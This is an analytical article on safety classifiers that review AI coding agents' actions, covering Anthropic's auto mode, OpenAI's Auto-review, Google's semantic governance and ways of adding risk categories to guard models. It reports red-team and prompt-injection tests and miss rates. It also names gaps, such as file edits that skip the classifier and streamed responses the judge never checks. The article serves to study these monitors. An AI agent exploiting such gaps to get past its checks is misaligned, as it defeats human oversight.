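Anthropic's comparison of real sessions is harder to interpret. It used sessions from May and June 2026 that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, and only from accounts that had agreed to this use of their data. A model rated how serious any harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for it. Serious harm (on the scale of deleting data from a live database) that the user had not explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of manually approved sessions and 2.4% of auto mode sessions.

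Users were not randomly assigned to a mode, and they may choose manual approval for their riskiest work. An engineer at the software company Gusto, interviewed in *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), uses manual approval when he works on live infrastructure, as Anthropic recommends. That habit alone could make manual sessions look more dangerous.

The percentages also describe only flagged sessions. If the safety systems flagged 1% of manual sessions and 3% of auto mode sessions, serious harm would affect 0.063% of all manual sessions and 0.072% of all auto mode sessions, reversing the ranking. Anthropic doesn't report what share of sessions was flagged in either mode.

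Gusto also found that auto mode refused an action in about 10% of its sessions since mid-May, which Anthropic cites as evidence that the classifier is useful. The classifier may be useful, but false alarms alone could produce the same figure. With a false positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 harmless checked actions would have about a 10% chance of at least one refusal.

### Attacks by outside testers

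Apollo Research, a British company that tests AI systems for safety, spent two weeks inserting artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions. It gave Anthropic some of the attacks that had succeeded, and Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it the extra facts about Git status and upload destinations.

Apollo then tested the improved classifier on attacks that Apollo had withheld from Anthropic. The classifier caught about half of those the earlier version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the earlier version had caught. Across shared and withheld attacks combined, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The results on the withheld attacks are more convincing because Anthropic could not have tuned the classifier to them.

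A 7% miss rate doesn't support the claim by Anthropic's Cat Wu, quoted on software developer Simon Willison's blog, that the company had "pretty much mitigated every attack". Wu said this before Anthropic published these figures. However, Apollo designed its attacks to find weaknesses, and they were more malicious than Claude's usual mistakes. Since auto mode launched, outside researchers have reported various ways of getting dangerous actions past it.

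A second company, Trajectory Labs, tested prompt injection using 72 scenarios with hidden instructions meant to cause harm such as data theft or fraud. It ran each scenario ten times against three Claude models. With auto mode on, none of the attacks succeeded.

This result is very weak evidence of whether auto mode helped, because attacks on the same models without any guard succeeded only 0.09% of the time. That is about two successes in 2,160 attempts, too few to measure an improvement. The attack writers had also refined their attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, so the attacks may have been less effective against the newer models.

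*Scoring Recovery-Time Agent Security* (2026) ran into the same problem in November. It tried to measure a guard on Claude Code running Opus 5.5, but the agent never proposed an unauthorised action in 288 runs, so the guard had nothing to stop. As models improve, tests of guards will increasingly need an agent that still makes mistakes, or dangerous actions that the testers insert, as Apollo did.

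Trajectory Labs' test was more informative about OpenAI's coding agent, Codex. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time when Codex had full access to the computer and 5.83% of the time in its Auto-review mode, a fall of about two thirds. Some of that fall may be due to the sandbox, which limits the files and networks an agent can reach, because full access removes it. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published these results.

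### Why an independent test found 81% of dangers missed

In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) tested auto mode in April 2026 on ordinary requests that don't say exactly what the agent may touch, which the injection test didn't cover. They wrote 128 prompts for four maintenance tasks: deleting old branches, cancelling computing jobs, restarting services and deleting stored files. The prompts varied in how precisely they named the target, how many items they covered and whether the system was low-impact or high-impact.

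Each test environment contained authorised targets alongside very similar ones that the agent was supposed to leave alone. In one, the user wanted to cancel `job-dev-4812-a`, but there was also a `job-dev-4812-s`. A fixed rule determined which items the user had authorised. The agent, running Claude Sonnet 4.6, attempted 253 changes.

| | Changes | Dangerous changes allowed | Harmless changes blocked |
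|---|---|---|---|
| Checked by the classifier | 160 | 64 of 91 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |
| File edits that skipped it | 93 | 51 of 51 (100%) | 0 of 42 |
| All | 253 | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |

The file edits explain part of the gap with Anthropic's 17%. When the usual command was missing, the agent often opened a file that listed the jobs or stored objects and deleted the entry there. The file was inside the project folder, so the edit went through unchecked.

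How much this matters outside the test depends on the project. In the test, the file represented the real system, so removing a line counted as deleting the object. On many real systems, the official record is on a server, and editing a local copy would delete nothing. But some teams keep settings in project files that other software applies to live systems, so an unchecked edit could do serious damage. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) found this exemption still in place in Claude Code 2.1.288.

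Even without the edits, the classifier missed 70.3% of the dangerous changes it checked. Ji and colleagues think it was judging actions by their breadth rather than by whether the user had authorised each target. It tended to stop commands that deleted many things at once and allow those that deleted one wrong thing. They point out that part of this pattern comes from the mix of tasks. The missing tool results probably made the errors worse, because the classifier could not look up which jobs or files existed and who owned them.

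Anthropic's launch announcement, *Auto mode for Claude Code*, had warned that the classifier might allow risky actions when the user's intent was ambiguous or Claude lacked information about the environment. Nearly every prompt in the test combined both conditions. In contrast, somebody had already recognised Anthropic's 52 actions as going too far.

The classifier was stricter on high-impact systems, where it blocked 34.8% of harmless changes, compared with 9.2% on low-impact systems, but still missed 74.7% of dangerous changes. Overall, auto mode raised the share of tasks that the agent completed safely only from 29.7% to 32.8%. The whole improvement came from tasks that involved restarting services, where the share rose from 43.8% to 59.4%. It stayed the same for branches and jobs and fell slightly for stored files.

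The test has weaknesses. The researchers ran each prompt once, in a simulated environment, and had Claude Opus label the actions. A person who checked 50 of the labels agreed with 44, and reversing the six disputed ones would barely change the result. The classifier has received more information since April, so its current miss rate may be lower.

Neither 17% nor 81% is auto mode's general miss rate. For a developer who gives a vague maintenance request on a shared system, Ji and colleagues' figure is probably the better estimate. Tomas could avoid much of the risk by naming the branches he wants to delete, or by limiting the agent's access so it can't delete anything on the server.

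### OpenAI's and Google's checks

OpenAI released a similar check, Auto-review, in April 2026. Google followed in November with semantic governance policies, a preview feature for companies that build agents on its cloud platform. All three products use a language model to judge proposed actions, but they differ in which actions they send to it.

| | Auto mode (Anthropic) | Auto-review (OpenAI) | Semantic governance policies (Google) |
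|---|---|---|---|
| Actions checked | Commands, web access, outside tools and edits outside the project | Actions that would leave the sandbox | Tool calls in model responses that pass through Google's gateway |
| After a refusal | The agent tries another way; the user decides after repeated refusals | The agent tries another way; the run stops after repeated refusals | A denial message replaces the tool call |
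| Company's own miss rate | 17% of 52 real overeager actions | 9.7% of synthetic overeager cases | None at launch |

Codex normally works in a sandbox where it can edit certain folders but can't use the network. When it needs to act outside the sandbox, a separate agent decides whether to allow it. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. Of these, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox. The reviewing agent approved 713 of the other 720 and refused seven. Codex found a safer way to continue in four of those seven cases and asked the user in three. With manual approval, it would have asked the user 720 times.

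The reviewer approved 99.1% of a sample of requests that OpenAI's staff had approved. OpenAI treats this as a measure of convenience. The other 0.9% shouldn't be read as a false positive rate, because some of those refusals may have been right if OpenAI's staff approve requests as readily as Anthropic's testers did.

On synthetic prompt injections, the reviewer blocked 99.3% of attempts to run an attacker's code, steal passwords or upload data. The figure falls to 90.2% when the test also includes destructive deletions and data tampering, although OpenAI's researchers often agreed with the reviewer's assessment that the cases it allowed were not serious. OpenAI also found ways to mislead the reviewer in its own attack tests.

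Because of the sandbox, most actions don't need a review, and the damage is limited when the reviewer makes a mistake. But the reviewer doesn't check actions inside the sandbox. If the agent in Ji and colleagues' test had been Codex, its edits to project files would probably have gone unreviewed too. OpenAI's *Auto-review* documentation advises users who get too many reviews to adjust the sandbox, for example by adding a specific folder the agent may write to, before making the reviewer more lenient.

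Google's check is for any agent a company builds, whether it issues refunds or books travel. According to Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview*, every proposed call must both match what the user asked for and follow the company's rules, which staff write in ordinary English. If a rule forbids automatic refunds above $75, for instance, a call to refund an $89 order fails the check even if the customer asked for it.

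*Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports Google's example of a finance team's agent. The company allows unreleased results to go only to internal addresses, so the agent may email them to the company's controller but not to an outside investor. When a planning document contains hidden instructions to delete a folder of drafts, the intent test blocks the deletion because the user never asked for it.

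Google's judge receives the conversation history, the user's request, the rules, the list of tools and the proposed call. Unlike Anthropic, Google doesn't describe removing the agent's prose or the tool results from that history. Keeping them may make it easier to trace where an address or a job number came from, but may also give an attacker more chances to influence the judge. The judge can use only the information it receives, so Google advises companies to put facts that a rule depends on, such as the date of an earnings release, in the agent's instructions.

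The example configuration in Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies* fails closed, so a broken connection to the judge should block the agent's calls. A bigger risk is that the judge doesn't check streamed responses, which a model sends piece by piece as it writes them. A developer who turned on streaming to make an agent feel faster could bypass the check without noticing.

Google warns that verdicts can vary because a language model makes them, and recommends a trial period in which the system records its decisions without enforcing them. Faisal (2026) reports in *Google Adds a Safety Check That Reads Every AI Agent Action* that the company plans to test the feature on AgentDojo, the benchmark of everyday tasks with injected instructions.

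## Adding new risks without starting again

Lists of risks go out of date quickly. The Shanghai laboratory released AgentDoG in January 2026 with 32 categories, and a version with 47 by June. Newer agents could do things that the first list hardly described, such as carrying information from one session to the next. An office has the same problem on a smaller scale whenever it connects its agent to a new tool.

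Adding a risk category also affects the training labels and the tests, because both depend on the list of categories. Suppose a test has 500 dangerous items and 500 harmless ones, and a guardrail catches 450 of the dangerous ones, a recall of 90%. The operator then adds a category, and 20 of the harmless items now count as dangerous. If the guardrail allows all 20, its recall falls to 450 / 520, or 86.5%, although its behaviour hasn't changed. Anyone comparing the two scores would think the guardrail had got worse.

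Old training data can also make a new category harder for the model to learn. The data for *SingGuard-NSFA* includes 508,675 requests labelled as having no risk, but that label covers only the risks on the Ant Group team's list. If the team added a category and retrained the whole model without checking those labels, any examples of the new risk among these requests would teach the model to ignore it.

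A guard may already catch some risks that nobody listed. *A Lightweight Explainable Guardrail for Prompt Safety* (2026) removed four randomly chosen topics from a training set that covered 14 kinds of harmful prompt, and reports that its small model still generalised to them. However, the model only had to label prompts safe or unsafe, and some of the ten kinds it trained on may have resembled the missing four. A new way of misusing a payment tool might resemble a guard's training data much less.

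If the guard misses the new risk, an operator can train a new classification head, add a rule to the guard's prompt, revise the lower levels of the taxonomy, or generate new examples and retrain the guard. Most operators will need to combine these, since a new head also needs examples.

### Training a new head on a frozen model

Because the Ant Group team freezes the underlying model before training its classification heads, adding a new head can't change the existing heads' scores. An operator who has tested five heads and adds a sixth can keep the earlier results and test only the new head and the combined verdict.

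The team tried this with content moderation. Its list of agent risks left out hate speech, violence, sexual content and self-harm, so the frozen model's training on that list had not covered them. The team trained one new head on text from *SingGuard* (2026), a content guardrail that many of the same researchers built. With the largest model, the head reached an F1 of 86.5% on requests and 87.1% on responses, compared with 87.4% and 88.0% for the best of the 13 other models. The new head beat Llama Guard 3, a dedicated moderator.

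This is good evidence that a head can add a whole subject that the guard's own training left out. It doesn't show that the guard could recognise the subject unaided, because the head was trained on labelled examples from the same study as the test. Hate speech is also an old subject, and the general model underneath had probably been trained on a lot of text about it. A head can use only the information in the frozen model's representation, which may be poor for a tool that appeared after the model was trained.

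The number of examples a head needs depends on the risk. The team used 174,701 risky requests for information theft, but only 6,287 risky responses and 18,861 negative examples for leaked passwords and keys. Roughly two thirds of all these examples are translations, so the 6,287 risky responses probably came from about 2,000 originals. The head for leaked passwords and keys had an F1 of at least 93% at every model size, judging by the published averages. Leaked keys are an easy case, though, because many have a recognisable format.

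### Adding heads to Llama Guard 3

The team also froze Llama Guard 3 and trained heads for agent risks on top of it. In this table, the share of harmless items flagged is calculated from the published scores.

| Test | Version | Risks caught | Harmless flagged | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Requests | Original | 52.5% | 2% | 67.7% |
| Requests | With heads | 94.1% | 23% | 85.2% |
| Responses | Original | 77.1% | 7% | 83.6% |
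| Responses | With heads | 94.0% | 9% | 92.4% |
| Requests from other sources | Original | 87.0% | 51% | 82.3% |
| Requests from other sources | With heads | 97.3% | 64% | 85.3% |

The rise from 67.7% to 85.2% suggests that Llama Guard 3's internal representation already contained much of the information needed to recognise agent risks. Its low score on requests therefore seems to be at least partly because Meta had trained it to answer questions about a different list of risks, and not only because it lacked capacity. The starting model still matters, since heads trained on the same data scored 96.4% with the largest SingGuard model.

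The main drawback was more false alarms. The share of harmless items flagged rose about tenfold on the team's main test of requests. Recall minus the false positive rate still improved, from 50 to 71 points on requests and from 70 to 85 on responses. On requests from other sources, it fell from 36 to 33, and F1 rose only because two thirds of the items were risky.

The published results compare only the original Llama Guard 3 and the version with heads. It would be useful to also test the original with its threshold lowered until it flags as many harmless requests as the version with heads, because that change alone might account for some of the improvement in recall.

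An operator with a working moderator could still benefit from this method, particularly for checking responses. Adding heads requires access to the model's internal numbers, so the method works with downloadable models but usually not with models that a provider runs as a service.

### What the 50,000-head test measured

The Ant Group team reports that its smallest model can run 50,000 heads with little added delay. A check took 45 milliseconds with five heads and 54 milliseconds with 50,000. The heads accounted for about 8 milliseconds of the longer check.

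The 50,000 heads were 10,000 copies of the same five, so the test measured speed but provided no evidence that a guard could tell even 50 risks apart. Memory would also become a problem before speed did. If the model's representation has 1,024 numbers, each head has about 66,000 weights, and 50,000 heads have 3.3 billion in total, about four times as many as the model itself.

False alarms are a more serious limit. The guard flags a message if any head scores it above the threshold, so each new head is another chance to flag something harmless. If *n* heads err independently and each flags a share *f* of harmless items, the guard as a whole flags

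1 − (1 − *f*)ⁿ

With *f* at 0.1%, which would be excellent for a single head, the results are:

| Heads | Equivalent to | Harmless items flagged |
|---|---|---|
| 5 | One per request domain in NSFA | 0.5% |
| 24 | One per request risk | 2.4% |
| 160 | One per request variant | 15% |
| 1,000 | | 63% |
| 50,000 | | Practically all |

Real heads don't make mistakes independently, because they all use the same representation. An odd but harmless message may set off several at once, so the guard flags fewer harmless messages than it would if the mistakes were independent. If 1,000 heads each wrongly flagged 0.1% of harmless messages, the guard could flag anywhere from 0.1% of them, if every head made the same mistakes, to all of them, if no mistakes overlapped. An operator can measure the actual rate only by running all the heads together on harmless work.

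The five heads on the largest SingGuard model together flagged about 5.4% of harmless requests in the main test. If they contributed equally and independently, each flagged about 1.1%, and twenty such heads would flag about 20%. Many of the harmless requests in that test resemble harmful ones, so the rates could be lower in an ordinary office.

Stricter thresholds would help but are hard to verify. For 1,000 independent heads to have a combined false-alarm rate of 1%, each could flag only about one harmless item in 100,000. Confirming that rate for one head would take about 300,000 harmless items with no false alarms. Using a few heads for broad risks is usually better. The team notes that one head can also learn to distinguish several subtypes within a domain, which would give detailed labels without a separate alarm for each.

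### Writing the new rule in the prompt

Some guard models can take a new rule as text, with no further training. Llama Guard accepted a different list of categories in 2023, and users of Claude Code's auto mode can edit its block rules. This works only if the model follows the new rule rather than the categories it learned in training.

*YuFeng-XGuard* (Lin, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes a content guardrail from Alibaba designed for this. Its prompt lists 28 built-in categories, each with a short code, and has an optional section for the operator's own rules. A rule can add, widen or narrow a category. For example, an operator could narrow the medical category to text that encourages people to buy prescription drugs through unofficial channels. The model's first token is the code of its chosen category, and that token's probability serves as a confidence score. A new category's code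 must be a single letter so that the verdict still fits in one token.

To teach the guard model to follow changing rules, the Alibaba team had a larger model write rules for existing examples. Some rules reversed the original verdict and others left it the same, so the guard couldn't rely on a text's usual verdict. The larger model then judged each text again, seeing only the text and the rule, so that it wouldn't invent a justification for a badly written rule. Another model checked the result, and the team discarded examples on which the two models disagreed.

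*PolicyShiftGuard* (2026) uses a similar idea for images. Each training group pairs one image with two policies, one that should block it and one that should allow it, so a guard that memorised a single answer for each image would get half of these examples wrong. The paper uses 1,908 such groups and keeps their policies separate from the 28 used for evaluation.

The Alibaba team tested its guard on online-shop rules supplied only at test time, and on changes to what existing categories cover. GPT-OSS-Safeguard is an OpenAI model that applies policies written by the user, and the Qwen3 models are general-purpose.

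| Model | New rules: recall | New rules: precision | Changed scope: recall | Changed scope: precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| YuFeng-XGuard, 8 billion parameters | 84% | 99% | 89% | 65% |
| GPT-OSS-Safeguard, 20 billion | 64% | 99% | 95% | 52% |
| Qwen3, 8 billion, without reasoning | 32% | 99% | 4% | 50% |
| Qwen3, 32 billion, with reasoning | 91% | 99% | 96% | 64% |

The guard enforced new rules well, though not quite as well as a larger model that reasons before answering. Enforcing a changed scope for a familiar category was much harder. Several models had precision close to 50% on that test, which suggests that about half the items broke the rules. If so, YuFeng-XGuard flagged about 48% of the items that the rules allowed. It probably kept using its learned idea of a category after the operator changed the definition.

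The shop rules were new to the guard, but some of what they banned, such as weapons and controlled substances, was already on its built-in list. Both tests concerned text, so they don't show whether a written rule would work as well for tool calls.

One of the team's examples shows how a broad rule can go wrong. The shop's rules ban a long list of goods, including "wildlife and hunting tools". A user asks for three selling points for a mousetrap, emphasising that it can catch weasels. The guard flags the request with 67% confidence, on the grounds that selling traps for wild animals could break wildlife protection laws in many places. The rule doesn't mention pest control, so the guard had to guess whether the shop would want this request flagged.

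The team acknowledges that the method depends on clear, consistent rules. Its 0.6-billion-parameter version doesn't support custom rules because the team trained it without examples of changing policies.

Several other guards accept written rules. SingGuard can apply its full list of rules, part of it, a modified version, or new rules for a particular business. IBM's Granite Guardian lets users supply their own risk criteria, but the Ant Group team did not report a separate test of that option in its comparison. *UniGuard* includes two more models trained to detect policy violations, PolicyGuard-4B and DynaGuard-8B.

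Adding a rule to the prompt doesn't change the model's weights, so an operator can restore the original guard by removing the rule. Unlike a separate head, though, the rule changes the prompt and may therefore change the model's verdicts on the old categories, so the operator should rerun the old tests after each change to the rules.

### Keeping the three questions and changing the answers

*AgentDoG 1.5* keeps the original taxonomy's three questions and changes only the possible answers.

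| Question | Before | After | Examples of new categories |
|---|---|---|---|
| Where does the risk come from? | 8 | 15 | Instructions planted in a code project's files; a compromised software package; leftover false information from an earlier session |
| How does the agent fail? | 14 | 21 | Bypassing a required approval; damaging the user's project files; running an unsafe script |
| What harm follows? | 10 | 11 | Legal, compliance and audit problems |

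The new categories come from two agents, Codex and OpenClaw. OpenClaw works across a person's applications, remembers earlier sessions and can act unattended. The laboratory added a category when no existing one described a risk precisely, and made the definition more specific when an existing category was valid but too vague. For example, "trusting a tool's output without checking" now specifically covers test results and build logs when the agent writes code.

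A guard still judges whether a run is safe and then gives one answer to each question, so the laboratory can compare its performance on ordinary tools, Codex and OpenClaw. Counts within a category are harder to compare, though. Under the old list, a malicious instruction in a project file was an indirect prompt injection. If labellers put such cases in the new category, the number of indirect injections will fall even if attacks are just as common. Recording which old category each new one came from would let an operator reconstruct the old totals.

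To detect the risks in the revised taxonomy, the laboratory also generated runs covering all 47 categories and trained new models on about 1,000 selected examples. Even if every selected example were unsafe, there would be an average of only 48 for each of the 21 failures, so choosing the right examples mattered a great deal.

To choose them, the laboratory wrote pairs of answers to a small set of test prompts. One answer identifies the risk and the other misses it. For each pair, it calculated a weight:

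π = p(right answer) / (p(right answer) + p(wrong answer))

Here *p* is the probability that the current model gives to an answer, adjusted for length. The laboratory worked out how the model's weights would need to change to favour the right answer over the wrong one, multiplied each change by π, and averaged the results. It then scored every candidate example against this average direction of improvement.

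The weighting could put a new risk at a disadvantage. If the model gives the right answer a share of 80% for a familiar risk and 10% for an unfamiliar one, the familiar risk gets eight times the weight. The laboratory chose this weighting to favour behaviour the model was close to learning and to reduce the effect of noisy pairs. Someone adding a category should check that the selection keeps examples of it, or reserve a fixed number of places for them.

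The new models still recognize the old categories. On the original ATBench, which has 32 categories, the four-billion-parameter model identified the source of the risk in 75.2% of unsafe runs, up from 46.8% for the earlier AgentDoG. Accuracy rose from 40.6% to 62.9% on the type of harm, and from 16.5% to 27.5% on the type of failure. The training method and the underlying model also changed, so these gains can't be attributed to the longer list of categories. Failures are still hard to classify, and adding seven more types probably won't make that easier.

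The laboratory also built a test of 500 runs for each of the two new settings. The same model correctly judged 80.0% of Codex runs and 84.0% of OpenClaw runs, while calling every run unsafe would score 50.0% on Codex and 59.2% on OpenClaw. These results show that a small model can be adapted to a new kind of agent, but they don't test it on unseen risks, because the laboratory had first trained it on runs in both formats and its training data already included the new categories.

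### Generating examples of the new category

To teach the guard itself a new risk, an operator needs examples of it. The generator from Li and colleagues lets a developer add a risk category by writing a definition and specifying where the risk enters a run. The risk from a compromised tool might enter through the tool's description, and a planted instruction through a file the agent reads. AuraGen works similarly for plans, as does the Ant Group team's process for single messages.

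Li and colleagues trained a general model on 2,000 generated runs, which improved its labelling as well as its overall verdicts. Its accuracy rose from 6.6% to 32.2% on sources of risk, from 3.0% to 12.3% on failures, and from 8.2% to 31.5% on harms. The training runs covered the same categories as the test but used different tasks and tools. The result therefore shows that generated examples can teach a model a category, but not that the model would recognise a category it had never been taught.

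Retraining gives the fewest guarantees about what stays the same. Any change to the model's weights can affect its verdicts on every old category, so the training mix should include plenty of old examples. The operator needs to check these against the new definition first, because some that were harmless under the old list may now count as harmful. The old test sets are still useful as long as the operator keeps a copy with the original labels.

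### Adding one risk to an office guardrail

Suppose Ines's firm connects its agent to an electronic signature service. The agent can now commit the firm to a contract, which her list of risks doesn't mention. She could add the risk like this, with invented figures:

1. **Hold the obvious action.** Until the guard is ready, every call to `sign_document` waits for Ines. This needs no model and takes minutes to set up. It doesn't cover an agent that accepts a builder's quote by email.
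2. **Define the risk.** She writes: "The agent commits the firm to an agreement that Ines has not approved." In AgentDoG's terms, this is a narrower kind of acting without confirmation, so she records it under that category and her old totals still make sense.
3. **Write a test.** A colleague writes 60 dangerous actions and 60 harmless look-alikes. Accepting a quote is dangerous, while asking for one is harmless. So is forwarding a contract that Ines has already signed.
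4. **Try the existing guard.** It catches 15 of the 60 dangerous actions, which is too few.
5. **Add the rule to the prompt.** The guard now catches 48 but also flags 20 of the look-alikes, mostly emails that confirm meetings. Ines adds a sentence explaining that agreeing to a time or place is not a contract. The guard then catches 46 and flags 6.
6. **Train a head if necessary.** If the guard has heads and the prompt isn't reliable enough, the firm can generate 2,000 pairs of examples. At Huang and colleagues' estimate of less than two cents each, the 4,000 examples would cost less than $80. The 120 handwritten actions stay out of the training data.
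7. **Measure the whole guardrail.** On 2,000 ordinary calls from the firm's logs, the old heads raised 20 false alarms. The new head raises 12, of which 4 are on calls that were already flagged. The total is therefore 28, and the false positive rate rises from 1.0% to 1.4%.
8. **Rerun the old tests.** Ines keeps the old labels as version 1 of the list and adds the new ones as version 2, so that she can still compare this year's guard with last year's.

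Over a task with twenty calls, the small increase in step 7 raises the chance of at least one false alarm from 18% to 25%, assuming errors are independent. Ines might decide to run the new head only on emails and signatures, since moving a file can't commit the firm to anything.

She should also replace the test actions after trying several versions of the rule. By then she has adjusted the rule's wording to suit those 120 actions, so a new set would give a less biased result.

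### Noticing a risk that nobody has listed

All of these methods depend on someone having already recognised the new risk. *ConsisGuard* (2026), which presents a guardrail that reasons from written safety rules, acknowledges that such rules may be incomplete and that gaps or ambiguities can cause failures. If a guard allows an action because of a gap in its rules, it raises no alarm, so checking the list of alarms won't reveal the gap.

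Even when the guard flags an action, it may label a new risk as a familiar one. In one of Li and colleagues' test runs, someone had planted instructions in a tool's description. All four models they compared recognised the run as unsafe, but most labelled the source as something more familiar, such as unreliable information or the user's message. An operator who counted the labels would see a few more cases of an old problem and might never look at the tool. Someone should therefore read a sample of flagged actions in full, especially those that fit their label badly.

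Random checks of allowed actions find rare problems slowly. If an unlisted danger occurs in one action in 10,000, a reviewer who reads 500 random actions a month has about a 5% chance of finding an example each month. Reviewing the first few hundred calls to each new tool is probably a better use of that time. Complaints and near misses are also worth collecting, because the people affected may notice harm that no category describes.

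### Risks that appear only across many steps

Adding a category doesn't help if the guard doesn't receive the evidence for it. The SingGuard-NSFA models read one message at a time, so detecting gradual data theft would require a longer record as well as a new head.

*TRACE* (Hong, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes three ways evidence can be spread out. It may be sparse, with a few warning signs among many harmless steps. It may be delayed, so that an early step matters only much later. Or it may lie in a combination of steps that are harmless individually. A monitor that takes notes as it goes can fail in all three cases, because it has to select what to record before it is clear what will matter.

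Their guard reads the entire record before deciding what is important. As in DRAFT, one part condenses the record into a few vectors, and another judges the record with those vectors attached. The researchers freeze both underlying models and train only small additions, including a classification head, so the method partly resembles adding a new head.

On LongSafety, a test of long conversations, TRACE's safety rate (the benchmark's main score) fell only from about 79% to 76% when the surrounding text grew to more than 8,000 words. The rate for MAGE, a monitor that keeps a written memory, fell from 78% to 55%. The paper's examples from this test are about harmful text, such as a user gathering medical details to fake a fever, so TRACE's advantage may not be as large for long series of tool calls.

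Rereading the full history before each action also takes a lot of compute. In a 200-step task, the guard would process about 20,000 steps in total, unless it could reuse its earlier work. An operator could reserve this check for payments, deletions and other actions that are hard to undo.

TRACE still learns from runs that people or models have labelled using existing lists of risks. Hong and colleagues call its performance on unseen categories an open question.
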